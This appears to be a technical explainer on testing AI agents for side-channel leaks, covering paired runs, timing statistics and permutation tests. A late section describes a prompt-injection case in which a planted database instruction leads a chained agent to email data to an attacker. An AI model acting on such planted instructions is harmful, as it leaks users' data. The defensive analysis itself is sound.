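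Counting characters instead of bytes is an easy mistake, especially in a bank assistant. Suppose the developer pads the text to 244 characters before converting it to JSON. An ordinary reply then takes exactly 256 bytes. But Python's JSON library writes a pound sign as six characters by default, so a reply with one amount in pounds takes 261 bytes and a reply with three takes 271. A test using only the letter x would miss this. The test texts should include currency signs, quotation marks, line breaks and emoji.

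The test also has to include any compression step, because compressing after padding undoes most of the padding. Compressing first and padding afterwards is safer, but the number of characters then no longer predicts a message's bucket. The developer can therefore test the padding step directly with blocks of 255, 256 and 257 bytes, and then run complete replies through both steps.

The best place to record message sizes is a fake network connection, just before encryption, because the software has by then added any headers, which can vary in length. The trace should list each message's size separately, because an eavesdropper can distinguish two 256-byte messages from one 512-byte message even though the totals are the same.

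### Generated inputs

Hand-picked pairs cover only the boundaries that the developer thought of. Property-based testing has the computer generate many inputs and check that a stated property holds for each. If the property fails, the tool looks for a smaller input that also fails, which makes the cause easier to see. With Hypothesis, a Python library for this, the test looks like this:

```
from hypothesis import example, given, strategies as st

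balances = st.integers(0, 999_999)

@given(balances, balances)
@example(999, 1000)
def test_any_two_balances(a, b):
    assert observe(a)[0] == observe(b)[0]
```

The `@example` line adds a pair that the test always tries, because random pairs often miss a threshold near the end of a range. If both balances were uniformly random, only 0.2% of pairs would straddle 1,000, and 100 pairs would have an 18% chance of including one that did. If the generator instead picked balances from 990 to 1,009, half the pairs would straddle the threshold, and ten pairs would almost certainly include one that did.

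In *Testing Noninterference, Quickly*, Hriţcu, Lampropoulos and colleagues (2014) measured how much the choice of generator affects the time it takes to find bugs. They used QuickCheck, a property-based testing tool for the language Haskell, to test a small simulated computer that labels its data as public or secret. They planted six bugs in its labelling rules, one at a time, and recorded how long QuickCheck took to find each.

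The inputs were whole programs. Two independently generated programs would almost never differ only in their secrets, so the researchers generated one program and changed only its secret values to get the second. An agent test should create its second user request and model script the same way.

| How the programs were generated | Planted bugs found within five minutes | Average time to find a missing label on a sum | Pairs discarded |
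|---|---|---|---|
| Random instructions | 4 of 6 | 83 seconds | 79% |
| Useful instructions made more likely | 4 of 6 | 5.3 seconds | 62% |
| Sequences of instructions that work together | 6 of 6 | 0.56 seconds | 65% |
| The same, with valid memory addresses favoured | 6 of 6 | 0.03 seconds | 59% |
| Each instruction checked by running the program so far | 6 of 6 | 0.0009 seconds | 4% |

Random instructions did badly because most programs crashed too early to leak anything. They ran for an average of 0.47 steps. The last method added an instruction only if it would not crash the program at that point. It ran about a seventh as many tests per second as the first method, but far more of them were useful.

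The same approach should work for agents, though the study did not test any. A generator that produces random tool calls will mostly leave out arguments, and the tools will reject those calls. A better generator would build the model's script one call at a time, run the agent after each addition, and keep only the calls that the tools accept. Favouring numbers that appear in the agent's code would help for the same reason that favouring valid addresses did.

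Hriţcu and colleagues then added jumps and procedure calls to the machine, which let secrets leak through control flow. They found that what the test compares also matters. One bug let a program delete the record of where to return after a procedure call. Comparing only the public memory at the end of each run did not find it within five minutes. With more varied starting states and a comparison of all the machine's public parts throughout the run, QuickCheck found it in an average of 1.8 seconds. Checking single steps from arbitrary small states took 0.4 milliseconds.

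An equivalent test for an agent interpreter would compare the public variables and their labels after every step, instead of waiting for an email to go out. This can find a wrong label even if the generated program never sends anything, but it takes more expertise because the developer has to work out which internal differences are harmless. Hriţcu and colleagues had to prove that their stricter properties implied the original one. They also warn that states can be too small, since one pair of bugs could not show up in a program with a single instruction.

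When a testing tool shrinks a failing case, it has to simplify both runs together. If it simplifies them separately, they soon differ in more than the secret, and comparing them becomes meaningless. Hriţcu and colleagues made every change to both programs at once. For one bug, this reduced typical failing programs from between 20 and 40 instructions to four. With an agent, the testing tool would remove the same call from both runs.

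There is some evidence that this kind of testing finds most bugs. When researchers later proved a variant of the first machine secure, they found no bugs that the tests had missed. But that machine was very simple, and an agent framework has many more places where a secret can affect what happens.

### What public test suites check

No public test suite or benchmark for AI agents appears to check whether a secret changes the number of requests in a loop or the length of a message. CaMeL, FIDES and similar projects may have such checks in their own tests.

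*AgentSecBench* (2026) is the closest in form to a paired-run test for side channels, because it defines a version of noninterference that permits authorised leakage. It keeps the trusted instruction and the authorised leakage fixed, changes the untrusted text that the agent reads, and tests whether a protected fact about the response or action can change. In one test, the untrusted text names an action that the user's policy doesn't allow. A paired-run test for side channels would keep the untrusted text fixed and change the secret.

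*PrivacyPeek* (2026) checks what information agents acquire. It gives an agent eight tools and up to six steps in each of 1,182 cases, and logs every call's name, arguments and return value. It then searches the returned content for items on a list prepared for that case. It checks each run separately, and an agent that fetched the overdraft terms would pass unless the page contained a listed item.

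*Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026) has 146 tasks in which credentials can leak through a route such as a log or a file that several agents share, even if the model removes them from its visible reply. These tasks also test for the secret itself. One of the routes is a gateway that writes every tool call and its arguments to disk, as the recording tools in a paired-run test do. These tools are safe with invented balances but would create a new leak if a developer left them running in the live service.

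PrivacyPeek would probably be the easiest of these benchmarks to adapt, because its logs already contain the names and arguments of the calls. A developer could create two versions of a case with different secrets, run both with a scripted model, and compare the logs. To cover the length channel, the logs would also need to record the size of each message as sent.

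## How can statistical tests check timing and random behaviour?

The paired-run tests above require identical traces, which is reasonable when only the balance differs between runs. But real response times and a live model's behaviour vary from run to run. A test that replaces the clock can still check one part of a timing mitigation exactly, namely the rule that decides when to send a reply.

### A simulated clock

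Suppose the assistant holds each reply until 15 seconds after the request. The test gives this code a fake clock that moves only when something waits:

```
class FakeClock:
    def __init__(self, now=0):
        self.now = now

    def sleep(self, seconds):
        self.now += seconds

def hold_reply(work, clock, hold=15):
    deadline = clock.now + hold
    work()
    clock.sleep(max(0, deadline - clock.now))
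    return clock.now

def released_at(seconds, **options):
    clock = FakeClock()
    return hold_reply(lambda: clock.sleep(seconds), clock, **options)

def test_release_does_not_depend_on_balance():
    assert released_at(3) == released_at(11) == 15
```

The function `work` stands in for the model and its tools, which take 3 seconds when the balance is healthy and 11 when it is low. Both replies go out at second 15, and the test finishes almost instantly. Setting `hold=0` removes the mitigation, so the replies go out at seconds 3 and 11 and the test fails. The test also fails if a developer starts the 15-second wait after the work ends, because the replies would then go out at seconds 18 and 26.

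Some designs need to be tested with more than one starting time. Suppose a fast reply takes 3 seconds and a slow one takes 11, and the server releases replies only at fixed marks on its own clock, 15 seconds apart. If a request arrives exactly at a mark, both replies go out at the next one. If it arrives seven seconds later, the fast reply is ready at second 10 and goes out at 15, while the slow one is ready at 18 and goes out at 30. The fast and slow replies go out at different times for 53% of arrival times, and a test whose clock always starts at zero misses all of these.

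A test with a simulated clock checks only the release logic. Computation takes no simulated time, so the test cannot detect that padding a long reply after the hold takes longer than padding a short one. The test also has no network and no queue in which one slow request delays the next. The developer supplied the 3-second and 11-second values, so the test cannot reveal a delay nobody knew about.

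Small pieces of code can be checked exactly in other ways. *DALC-CT* (2026) records and compares the instructions that a compiled program executes under different secrets, without measuring time. The test suite in *Zirah* (2026), which describes a device for signing data, fails if any code that handles the key contains a division instruction, because division on that processor takes longer for some numbers than for others. Checks like these could cover the code that holds and pads replies, but not a model on another company's server, which the developer has to measure instead.

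### Measured times

The best-known tool for measuring timing leaks is dudect, which Reparaz, Balasch and Verbauwhede released in 2017 for cryptographic code. It runs a function many times on two classes of input, such as one fixed secret and a stream of random ones, and records how long each run takes. It then computes Welch's t statistic,

t = (x̄₀ − x̄₁) / √(s₀²/n₀ + s₁²/n₁),

where x̄ is the average time in each class, s² the variance and n the number of runs. The denominator estimates how much the difference between the averages would vary by chance, known as its standard error.

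The usual rule is to report a leak if t is above 4.5 or below −4.5. *Beyond TVLA* (Mikulec, Breier and Hou, 2026) puts the false-alarm rate of this rule at about 6.8 in a million. When dudect's developers applied the rule to two versions of the AES cipher, t exceeded 100 for one that uses lookup tables and stayed below 4.5 through several million measurements for one designed to avoid timing leaks.

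The runs have to come in random order. If all the low-balance runs came first, a server that slowed down during the day would look like a leak.

The choice of classes also affects whether the test finds a leak. If the random balances range up to a million, 99.9% of them are above 1,000, so comparing them with a fixed balance of 1,100 would reveal almost nothing about a branch at 1,000. Comparing 900 with 1,100 is better because it tests both sides of the branch. *FreeSBee* (2026), which times AES decryption on a small processor, repeats the comparison with several fixed inputs because some reveal a leak sooner than others.

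A timing test needs a positive control, a known leak that it must find. Zirah's suite includes a comparison function that stops at the first wrong byte. For the assistant, the developer could add a 5-millisecond delay when the balance is low. The developer should also compare a balance with itself, as in the paired-run tests.

### Spread and tails

Welch's test compares averages, so it can miss other differences. Suppose a tool always answers in 200 milliseconds when the balance is healthy, and in either 150 or 250 milliseconds, equally often, when it is low. Both averages are 200, but the timing of a single answer reveals whether the balance is low. Dunsche, Erinola and colleagues (2025), in *SILENT*, point out that dudect can likewise miss the difference between two bell curves with the same centre but different widths.

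The Kolmogorov–Smirnov test detects this kind of leak. Its statistic is the largest difference, at any moment, between the two classes in the share of runs that have finished. At 160 milliseconds, half of the low-balance runs have finished and none of the others have, so the statistic is at least 0.5. The Anderson–Darling test adds up the differences over the whole range and gives more weight to the extremes. Mikulec and colleagues used it on the power consumption of a small neural network that shuffles its calculations for protection. It detected leaks that Welch's test had missed, and these leaks helped recover part of one of the network's weights.

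Neither test is efficient for rare events. In the earlier example, 2% of replies missed the 15-second limit when the balance was low and 0.1% when it was healthy. If nothing else differs, the largest gap is 0.019, and the Kolmogorov–Smirnov test needs about 10,000 runs per class to find that gap significant at the 5% level. Counting late replies and comparing the two proportions detects the leak 90% of the time with about 600 runs per class. A developer who knows which event might leak should therefore test for it directly.

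Some tests discard rare events. Zirah's suite compares the times twice, once with every call and once without the slowest, which mostly reflect interruptions by other programs. Discarding the slowest calls reduces noise but would also remove a leak that appears only in them, so the first comparison is still necessary. The tool RTLF compares only the deciles, the points that divide the runs into tenths, so a leak confined to the slowest 2% of runs doesn't change any of them.

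### How many runs are enough?

Suppose a leak changes the mean response time by 5 milliseconds, and response times have a standard deviation of 50 milliseconds. With 100 runs per class, the standard error of the difference is 50 × √(2/100) = 7.1 milliseconds, which is larger than the leak. A test at the 5% level, which reports a leak when t is beyond 1.96 in either direction, then detects this leak only 11% of the time, so the leaking agent usually passes. Detecting the leak 90% of the time takes about 2,100 runs per class, according to the sample-size formula given for message lengths.

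| Runs per class | Standard error | Chance of detection, 5% level | Chance of detection, threshold of 4.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| 100 | 7.1 ms | 11% | Under 0.01% |
| 500 | 3.2 ms | 35% | 0.2% |
| 2,100 | 1.5 ms | 90% | 10% |
| 10,000 | 0.7 ms | Nearly 100% | 99% |

An attacker with 10,000 samples of each kind sees an unmistakable gap of about seven standard errors. The developer can pass the test with 100 runs and still be exposed to that attacker.

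The last column shows how demanding dudect's strict threshold is. The threshold suits cryptographic functions, which take microseconds and can run hundreds of thousands of times. *Systematic Timing Leakage Analysis of NIST PQDSS Candidates* (2025), which tested proposed digital signature schemes, used 210,000 measurements by default. If an agent takes 15 seconds per reply, even 2,100 runs for each of two classes take 17.5 hours when run one after another.

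Reducing the noise usually takes less effort than adding runs. If the developer can lower the standard deviation from 50 milliseconds to 5 by measuring the tool alone, about 21 runs per class are enough.

Dunsche and colleagues measured how an observer's position affects the number of measurements needed to detect a timing leak. They built a website whose login check took longer for existing usernames, by roughly 11 microseconds when measured on the same machine. Detecting this difference took about 1,500 measurements on the same machine, 1,200 on the local network and 7,000 over a nearby internet connection. Between continents, there was too much noise to plan the test from 10,000 measurements. Using the leak size measured locally, they estimated that the test would need about 400,000.

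The SILENT tool uses a small pilot to estimate how many measurements a test needs, but the estimate is only a rough guide. For a known leak of about 20 processor cycles in Kyber, an encryption scheme, it estimated from a pilot of 300 measurements that 785 would detect the leak 90% of the time, but they detected it 69% of the time. Planning for a leak of 15 cycles instead raised the estimate to 1,826 measurements, which detected the leak 92% of the time. It is therefore sensible to plan for a leak somewhat smaller than the one expected.

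### Equivalence testing

A test can find no significant difference even when the times differ, which may be why the timing audit by Gu and colleagues missed DeepSeek's cache. With 250 samples per class and the audit's strict significance level of 10⁻⁸, the Kolmogorov–Smirnov statistic has to reach about 0.27 to be significant, so the audit could miss quite a large difference.

*FreeSBee* describes Welch's test as determining whether two distributions are "statistically equivalent", which it can't do. To test for equivalence, the developer first sets a margin, the largest acceptable difference. An equivalence test then assumes that the real difference is at least that large, and passes only if the data rule this out.

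In the simplest version, which consists of two one-sided tests, the developer computes a 90% confidence interval for the difference in average times. The test passes at the 5% level if the whole interval lies within the margin on both sides of zero. Suppose the margin is 5 milliseconds, the standard deviation is again 50, and the observed difference is 2:

| Runs per class | 90% interval for the difference | Ordinary test | Equivalence test, 5 ms margin |
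|---|---|---|---|
| 100 | −9.6 to 13.6 ms | No difference found | Fails |
| 2,200 | −0.5 to 4.5 ms | No difference found | Passes |

The ordinary test gives the same result in both rows, though only the second has enough data to support a conclusion. With 100 runs, the equivalence test could not pass even if the observed difference were zero. A developer who collects too little data will therefore fail the equivalence test rather than be falsely reassured.

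Choosing the margin requires some judgement about the attacker. For an attacker with 10,000 samples per class, a difference of 1 millisecond is 1.4 standard errors, which is weak evidence. But a developer needs about 54,000 runs per class to show that the difference is below 1 millisecond, and an attacker closer to the server may face less noise than the developer did. Even in cryptography, experts disagree about what is negligible. Dunsche and colleagues cite one estimate that attackers can't exploit differences under 100 nanoseconds, and another that a single processor cycle can be detectable on a local network.

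SILENT also lets the developer state a margin, but it keeps the ordinary burden of proof by assuming that the difference is within the margin and reporting a violation only if the data contradict this. This is meant to prevent alarms about leaks too small to matter. However, a result of "No Violation" from a small sample doesn't show that the leak is small. SILENT can also still raise alarms about leaks below the margin. With a margin of 40 cycles, it reported the 20-cycle leak in 11% of 1,000 trials, although its theory predicts almost no alarms that far below the margin when there is enough data.

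An equivalence test on averages would pass the tool that answers in 150 or 250 milliseconds. To check the spread as well, the developer can apply a margin to several percentiles, such as the 10th, 50th, 90th and 99th, and require all of them to pass. This doesn't need the usual correction for multiple tests, because each added condition makes passing harder.

### Timing tests in a build

Software teams usually run their tests on every change and block the change if any test fails. A statistical test at the 5% level will block one harmless change in twenty. With twenty independent tests, 64% of harmless changes will fail at least one.

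The simplest correction, named after Bonferroni, divides the significance level by the number of tests. With twenty tests, each uses a level of 0.25%, and detecting the 5-millisecond leak 90% of the time takes about 3,700 runs per class instead of 2,100. The Benjamini–Hochberg correction is less strict because it limits the expected share of false alarms among all alarms, instead of the chance of any false alarm. It is better suited to a report that somebody will read than to a rule that blocks changes automatically.

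Developers often rerun a failed test and accept a pass, which makes a timing test less likely to detect a leak. If a single run finds a leak 90% of the time, allowing one retry lowers that to 81%, and allowing two lowers it to 73%. Checking the results early has the opposite effect and causes more false alarms. A developer who tests at the 5% level after each of ten equal batches, and stops at the first significant result, gets a false alarm about 19% of the time. *FreeSBee* recalculates t after every new measurement to watch for trends, which is harmless only if the developer waits until the planned end to decide whether the test passes.

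The first few runs are often slow because the program is still loading data and opening connections, so the test should discard a fixed number of them. Shared machines are harder to deal with because other people's jobs can slow a whole series of runs. To reduce noise, the signature study ran its tests directly on the hardware, without Docker containers.

A slow spell also makes neighbouring measurements similar, so 1,000 of them carry less information than 1,000 independent ones. Dunsche and colleagues found that existing tools raise too many false alarms on such data. For example, RTLF had reported a leak in the encryption library mbedTLS that nobody could find in its code. The method Dunsche and colleagues developed resamples neighbouring measurements in blocks to account for their similarity, and it detected no leak in the same data.

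Given the cost, one reasonable arrangement is to run the simulated-clock tests on every change and the measured ones overnight on a dedicated machine.

### Random choices by a live model

A scripted model makes the same choices every time, so it can't show how a real model responds to a secret. *Eight in Ten LLMs Leak System-Prompt Secrets* (2026) describes a model that frequently refused to repeat a list of strings if the list contained part of its secret, and complied if it didn't. The secret leaks through how often the model refuses, so a single refusal proves little.

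To test the bank assistant for such leaks, the developer runs it many times at each of two balances, in random order, and counts how often each complete trace occurs. The developer can then measure the difference between the balances as half the sum of the absolute differences in frequency, the distance Garby and colleagues used in their theorem. In a finite sample, this distance is almost never zero, even when the balance has no effect on the trace. If the assistant had the same twenty equally likely traces at both balances, 100 runs at each would give an average distance of about 25%.

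A permutation test works out how large a distance chance alone would produce. It pools the traces, shuffles them, deals them into two new groups and measures the distance again:

```
import random
from collections import Counter

def gap(low, high):
    a, b = Counter(low), Counter(high)
    return sum(abs(a[t] - b[t]) for t in a | b)

def p_value(low, high, shuffles=9999):
    observed, pool, extreme = gap(low, high), low + high, 1
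    for _ in range(shuffles):
        random.shuffle(pool)
        extreme += gap(pool[:len(low)], pool[len(low):]) >= observed
    return extreme / (shuffles + 1)
```

The code assumes the same number of runs at each balance. It doesn't divide the gap to get a distance, because dividing wouldn't change the comparison. Suppose the assistant fetches the overdraft terms in 12 of 40 runs at the low balance and in 4 of 40 at the high one. About 4.8% of shuffles produce a gap at least that large, so the result is just significant at the 5% level. With 100 runs at each balance and the same proportions, the share of such shuffles falls below 0.1%.

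This test also has the correct false-alarm rate when neighbouring runs resemble each other, provided the developer put the runs in random order. The same procedure therefore works for measured times, with the t or Kolmogorov–Smirnov statistic in place of `gap`.

Comparing whole traces doesn't work if they rarely repeat. Traces that include exact message sizes may all be unique, in which case every shuffle gives the same gap as the real data and the test can never find a leak. Gao, Liang and Guestrin (2024) met this problem in *Model Equality Testing*, when they checked whether companies were serving the language models they claimed to. They scored how similar two texts are by counting the positions at which they match, then compared the similarity within each group with the similarity between groups. With an average of ten samples for each of 25 prompts, this typically detected an altered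 model 77% of the time, which was better than looking for exact matches.

Position-by-position matching has a drawback for agents, because one extra call at the start shifts all the later ones. A developer could instead compare summaries of each run, such as the number of calls to each tool. To check whether a new version of an agent behaves differently from the old one, *AgentAssay* (2026) reduces each run to 14 numbers, including how often the agent used each tool and how many steps it took. A summary misses any leak in the details it omits, such as exact message sizes.

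The test should also use many wordings of the user's request. A thousand runs of one question about a holiday are good evidence about that question only. *AgentDiff* (2026) accounts for the grouping of runs by resampling whole models and whole questions instead of single runs. In a permutation test, the developer can shuffle the balances separately within each wording. *Characterizing LLM Agent Behaviors in Module Shadowing Environments* (2026), which studies whether agents run planted code, similarly shuffles its conditions within each model.

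Cached prompts can distort timings from a live service. *Whisper Leak* avoided this by inserting extra spaces at random places, so that no two queries were identical, and by mixing the two kinds of query together. Live tests also cost money. A single test in the audit by Gu and colleagues could use 34 million tokens, which cost between $1.69 and $8.44 for the chat models they tested in 2024.

### Training a classifier to find the secret

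Instead of choosing what to compare, a developer can let a classifier look for differences. Lopez-Paz and Oquab (2016), in *Revisiting Classifier Two-Sample Tests*, describe the procedure:

1. Label each trace with the secret that produced it.
2. Shuffle the traces and split them into a training set and a held-out set.
3. Train a classifier on the training set to predict the label.
4. Measure its accuracy on the held-out set.
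5. Calculate how likely that accuracy would be if the classifier were guessing.

If there is no leak and there are equally many traces of each kind, the classifier's number of correct answers is distributed like the number of heads in fair coin tosses. Suppose the classifier is right for 116 of 200 held-out traces, or 58%. Guessing would do at least this well about 1.4% of the time. The 95% confidence interval for the accuracy is 51% to 65%, so there is probably a leak, but it could be tiny.

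The interval is more useful than a pass or fail result because it describes what an attacker could do with one session. The best possible accuracy is one half plus half the distance between the two distributions, so an accuracy of 58% implies a distance of at least 16%, and a better classifier might reveal a larger one. *AgentSecBench* similarly defines leakage as how much an efficient attacker can outperform random guessing, and warns that another attack may succeed even if the chosen one finds nothing.

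Detecting small leaks again takes large samples. If the classifier's true accuracy is 55%, Lopez-Paz and Oquab's formula implies that a test on 200 held-out traces detects the leak about 41% of the time. Detecting it 90% of the time takes about 850 held-out traces, plus the traces used for training. Using more of the data for training can produce a better classifier but leaves fewer traces to test it on.

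The developer should hold out whole wordings of the request, as *Whisper Leak* does, so that the accuracy reflects wordings the classifier hasn't seen. If one balance has more runs than the other, plain accuracy is misleading, because always naming the more common balance is right more than half the time. *Information Leakage Detection through Approximate Bayes-optimal Prediction* (2024), which looks for timing leaks in encrypted web servers, handles this by applying Fisher's exact test to the table of predicted and true labels. The test checks whether the predictions depend on the true labels.

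None of the agent tools described here comes ready to test for side channels. AgentAssay is perhaps the closest, because it already compares two sets of random runs. A developer would have to give it runs at two balances instead of runs of two agent versions, and add message sizes and times to its summary of each run.

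## What does a passing test leave unproved?

A paired-run test that uses n pairs of secrets checks n equations:

record(test_run(pᵢ, sᵢ)) = record(test_run(pᵢ, sᵢ′)), for i = 1, …, n.

`record` keeps whatever the test logs, and `test_run` runs the current code with fake tools and a scripted model. Noninterference requires the same equality for every public input and every pair of secrets, in what the observer actually sees of the live system rather than in the log of a test run. A pass therefore shows only that the recorded observables did not differ for the tested pairs in the test environment. A pass on an equivalence test is weaker still, because it shows only that the difference is below a chosen margin at a stated confidence.

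### Inputs nobody tried

Suppose the assistant also checks a four-digit PIN, and a developer left in a debugging shortcut that fetches a status page when the PIN is 4071. An eavesdropper who knows about the shortcut and sees the fetch learns that customer's whole PIN.

A test that draws two PINs at random exposes the shortcut only if exactly one of them is 4071, which has a probability of 2 × 0.0001 × 0.9999, or about 0.0002. With 1,000 random pairs, the chance of finding the leak is 1 − 0.9998¹⁰⁰⁰, or about 18%. Raising it to 95% takes about 15,000 pairs, or 30,000 runs. Running all 10,000 PINs once and comparing every trace with the first takes a third as many runs and is certain to expose the shortcut.

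Testing every possible value of a secret is practical only when there are few values and each test is fast. Testing a million balances takes 17 minutes with a scripted model at a millisecond each, but 174 days with a live agent that needs 15 seconds per reply. Either way, the result covers only one wording of the user's request.

When random pairs all pass, the developer can still put an upper limit on the failure rate. If a fraction q of all pairs would fail, n independent pairs all pass with probability (1 − q)ⁿ. This probability drops to 5% when q is about 3/n, because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is about −3. If all n pairs pass, the failure rate is below about 3/n at 95% confidence. For 1,000 pairs the limit is 0.3%, well above the PIN shortcut's rate of 0.02%, so 1,000 passes don't rule out the shortcut.

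The limit applies only to the distribution the developer drew the pairs from. An attacker who plants instructions in a web page chooses part of the input, and has no reason to make it typical. Narisetty and colleagues describe twelve defences against prompt injection, most of which had let through almost none of a fixed set of attacks. Attackers who adapted to the defences got past most of them more than 90% of the time.

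Narisetty and colleagues then tested Progent, which checks each tool call against a set of rules. Progent cut the average success rate of standard attacks from 25.8% to 4.2%, and an attack written to get around it succeeded 2.6% of the time. That is mildly encouraging, but the latter test used a single attack template against one small model.

Attackers are also more likely to succeed if they can keep trying. Narisetty and colleagues cite Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5, which show that attacks on coding agents succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt and 63.0% with a hundred.

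### What the log left out

The earlier test of prefetching passes because the agent fetches the overdraft terms on every run. However, its log contains only tool calls, and three other things still depend on the balance:

| What varies | Balance of 900 | Balance of 1,100 | Who can observe it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Length of the reply | 18 characters | 4 characters | An eavesdropper on the user's connection |
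| Calls to the model | 3 | 2 | An eavesdropper between the agent and the model |
| Time to reply | Longer by one model call | Shorter | Both |

The stored copy avoids a web request, but the model still has to request the page and then run again once it has the text. Putting the overdraft terms in the first prompt could remove that extra model call. Padding the reply could hide its length, and delaying it could hide its timing. To check any of this, the developer has to log model calls, bytes and times as well as tool calls.

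A longer log helps only with the observables someone thought to include. The developer assumes that the list of channels is complete, and no test built from that list can check this assumption.

### From the test to the live service

A test can miss a leak when its fake tools are simpler than the real ones. In the earlier transfer test, the fake bank refuses a transfer by raising an exception. Suppose the real bank returns an error code instead, and the library that sends the request treats the error as temporary and retries twice. An eavesdropper then counts three requests when the balance is too low and one when it is high enough. The test passes because the fake replaced the library along with the bank. Running the real library against a fake server would expose the retries.

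A passing test can also miss leaks caused by proxies and caches. A proxy may compress replies after the agent has padded them, which can undo the padding. A test that starts with empty caches can't show whether one customer's request speeds up another's.

The best-documented failures of this kind come from cryptography, where programmers write "constant-time" code, whose branches and memory addresses never depend on a secret. To choose between x and y without a branch, they compute

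result = (y AND mask) OR (x AND NOT mask),

where the secret makes the mask either all ones or all zeros. But a compiler, which translates source code into machine instructions, may replace this with anything that produces the same result, including a branch.

In *Breaking Bad*, Schneider, Lain and colleagues (2024) measured how often this happens. They compiled eight cryptographic libraries for six types of processor, using many versions of two common compilers. They ran each program with different secret keys, kept all the randomness fixed, and compared the traces, much as a paired-run test does. Of 5,716 compiled programs, 429 (7.5%) had control flow that depended on the secret, and 368 (6.4%) had memory accesses that did.

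HACL*, one of the affected libraries, came with a formal proof that its source code was free of such leaks. The compiler LLVM recognised the masking arithmetic as a choice between two values. For two types of processor, it produced a branch, and for two others, a memory address that depended on the secret.

The 7.5% applies to the combinations the researchers tried, not to the software people use, and common processor types did better than rare ones. The researchers also counted every dependence on a secret, whether or not an attacker could exploit it. On the other hand, they recorded only eight traces per test and acknowledge that their method can find leaks but can't prove there are none.

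At least one such leak was exploitable. In *Compiler-introduced timing leak in Kyber reference implementation*, Purnal (2024) reported that recent versions of the compiler Clang added a secret-dependent branch to the published code for the encryption scheme Kyber. Purnal recovered a secret key in about ten minutes by timing the program on a laptop.

The leak depended on the compiler's settings. Clang produced the leaking branch when set to minimize code size. At its usual settings for speed, the program contained both a leaking version and a safe one, and appeared to run the safe one. A developer could therefore test the fast build, see it pass, and ship a small build that leaks. The entry for this leak in NVD, the US government's database of software vulnerabilities, cautions against relying on compiler settings as a workaround.

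Few agent developers need to worry about their compiler, because a single branch takes negligible time compared with a call to a language model. But an agent's messages also pass through layers that other people wrote, and testing the agent's own code can't show what those layers do.

### Updates

A scripted model never changes, so a test built on it keeps passing after the provider replaces the real model. Suppose the old model looked up only the overdraft terms when the balance was low, and the new one also looks up emergency loans. Prefetching covers the overdraft page but not the loan page, so the request for the loan page reveals that the balance is low. Adding a new tool can cause the same kind of leak.

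Schneider and colleagues found one widely copied piece of masking code that stayed safe under every compiler they tried. But after small, harmless-looking edits, such as moving a few lines into a separate function, compilers made the program depend on the secret.

A new mitigation can even break an old one. OpenSSH, a program for logging in to remote computers, sends fake keystroke packets to hide when the user is typing. The release notes from OpenSSH (2024) describe a logic error in how versions 9.5 to 9.7 sent fake and real packets, which let an eavesdropper pick out the real ones.

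The same error damaged a much older protection. When a user types a password, the server normally has nothing to send back for display, so an eavesdropper could recognize password entry by the lack of responses. The server had long sent fake responses to prevent this, but the new feature made them ineffective. After adding a mitigation, developers should therefore rerun the tests for all the others.

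### Agents that pass one at a time

Developers often test agents separately and then connect them. Peters-Gill and colleagues show how this approach can fail for a property called control-flow integrity. An agent has this property if its tool calls always follow a plan fixed by the user's instruction and other trusted information. A single CaMeL agent has this property.

The researchers connected three CaMeL agents. An orchestrator received the user's request and delegated work to a database agent and a notification agent, which could send emails and Slack messages. The user asked the system to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. To simulate an attack, the researchers had put an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address.

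The database agent and the orchestrator followed their plans because their planning models did not read the data. But the orchestrator then put the summary, including the planted instruction, into its message to the notification agent. That agent treated the whole message as an instruction from its user and planned an extra email to the attacker.

Peters-Gill and colleagues also prove that every hierarchy of two or more such agents lacks control-flow integrity if any of its tools returns untrusted data. The proof assumes that a user can ask any agent to call any of its tools and pass on the result.

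A large test can easily miss this flaw. The researchers tested five models, running 949 attacks with each on systems of individually protected agents. Attacks succeeded 0.5% of the time with GPT-4.1 and 0.4% of the time with Gemini 2.5 Pro, but never with the other three models. A developer using one of those three would have seen all 949 tests pass, even though the system provably lacks the property.

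Their remedy, multi-CaMeL (October 2026), has agents communicate through two channels, one for instructions and one for data that the receiving agent's planning model can't read. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output.

No attack succeeded against multi-CaMeL with any of the models. For zero successes in 949 runs, the 3/n rule gives an upper limit of 0.32% on the attack success rate. The researchers report 0.4%, mainly because they use a two-sided interval. But the 949 runs are every combination of user task and attack within the benchmark's four settings, so they are not a random sample of what an attacker might try. The argument about the interpreter is better evidence, although CaMeL's untaken-branch flaw means the current software may not fully enforce the interpreter's rule.

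This result covers integrity, or what untrusted data can make agents do. It does not cover what an observer can learn about a secret. As with a single CaMeL agent, a branch already in the plan can still reveal the balance.

Secrets can also leak when labels are lost between agents. Suppose the orchestrator writes "the customer is short of money" in a message, and the receiving agent labels all its instructions public. The secret then loses its label, just as the planted instruction lost its "untrusted" label. Multi-CaMeL keeps labels attached to the values in its data channel, which should help, but the researchers tested it without any confidentiality policies.

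Two agents can also leak a secret together when neither leaks it alone. Suppose one agent always fetches the same two pages, in an order set by the account balance and a random coin toss. If the balance is low, the agent fetches the overdraft page first on heads and second on tails, and if the balance is healthy, it does the opposite. Each order then occurs half the time, whatever the balance is. A second agent uploads debugging records that contain the result of the coin toss, which doesn't depend on the balance either. Both agents pass their own tests, but an observer who sees the order and the coin toss can always tell whether the balance is low.

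### What tests are good for

Developers mostly write tests to catch mistakes, and side-channel tests do this well. A failing pair of runs also gives the developer an example to debug. A paired-run test could have caught the OpenSSH error by comparing packet times for two different typing rhythms.

Automatic tests are also a practical response to updates. In the discussion after Purnal's report, the cryptographer Daniel J. Bernstein announced that the benchmarking project SUPERCOP had begun checking 1,307 implementations described as avoiding secret-dependent branches and memory addresses. The project repeats the checks on each machine that regularly runs its benchmarks. The project includes one implementation designed to leak, and the check flags it with every compiler tested.

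A test also documents what the developer meant by "closed". In the earlier example, the function `outsider` precisely describes the observer, so a reviewer can object that this observer should see model calls too. A claim like "the agent protects your balance" is much harder to challenge in this way.

### Other kinds of evidence

Each stronger kind of evidence removes some of a unit test's assumptions and keeps or adds others:

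| Evidence | What it adds to a unit test | What it still assumes |
|---|---|---|
| Recordings of real traffic | Real tools, proxies and networks | The recording covers everything the observer sees, on typical inputs |
| Automated search | Channels missing from the developer's list | The search covers everything the observer could measure |
| A trained attacker | Patterns that nobody thought to compare | Real attackers have no better methods or data |
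| A leakage limit from counting outcomes | A maximum that holds for every attacker | The list of distinguishable outcomes is complete |
| A machine-checked proof | Every input and every secret | The mathematical model matches the real system and observer |

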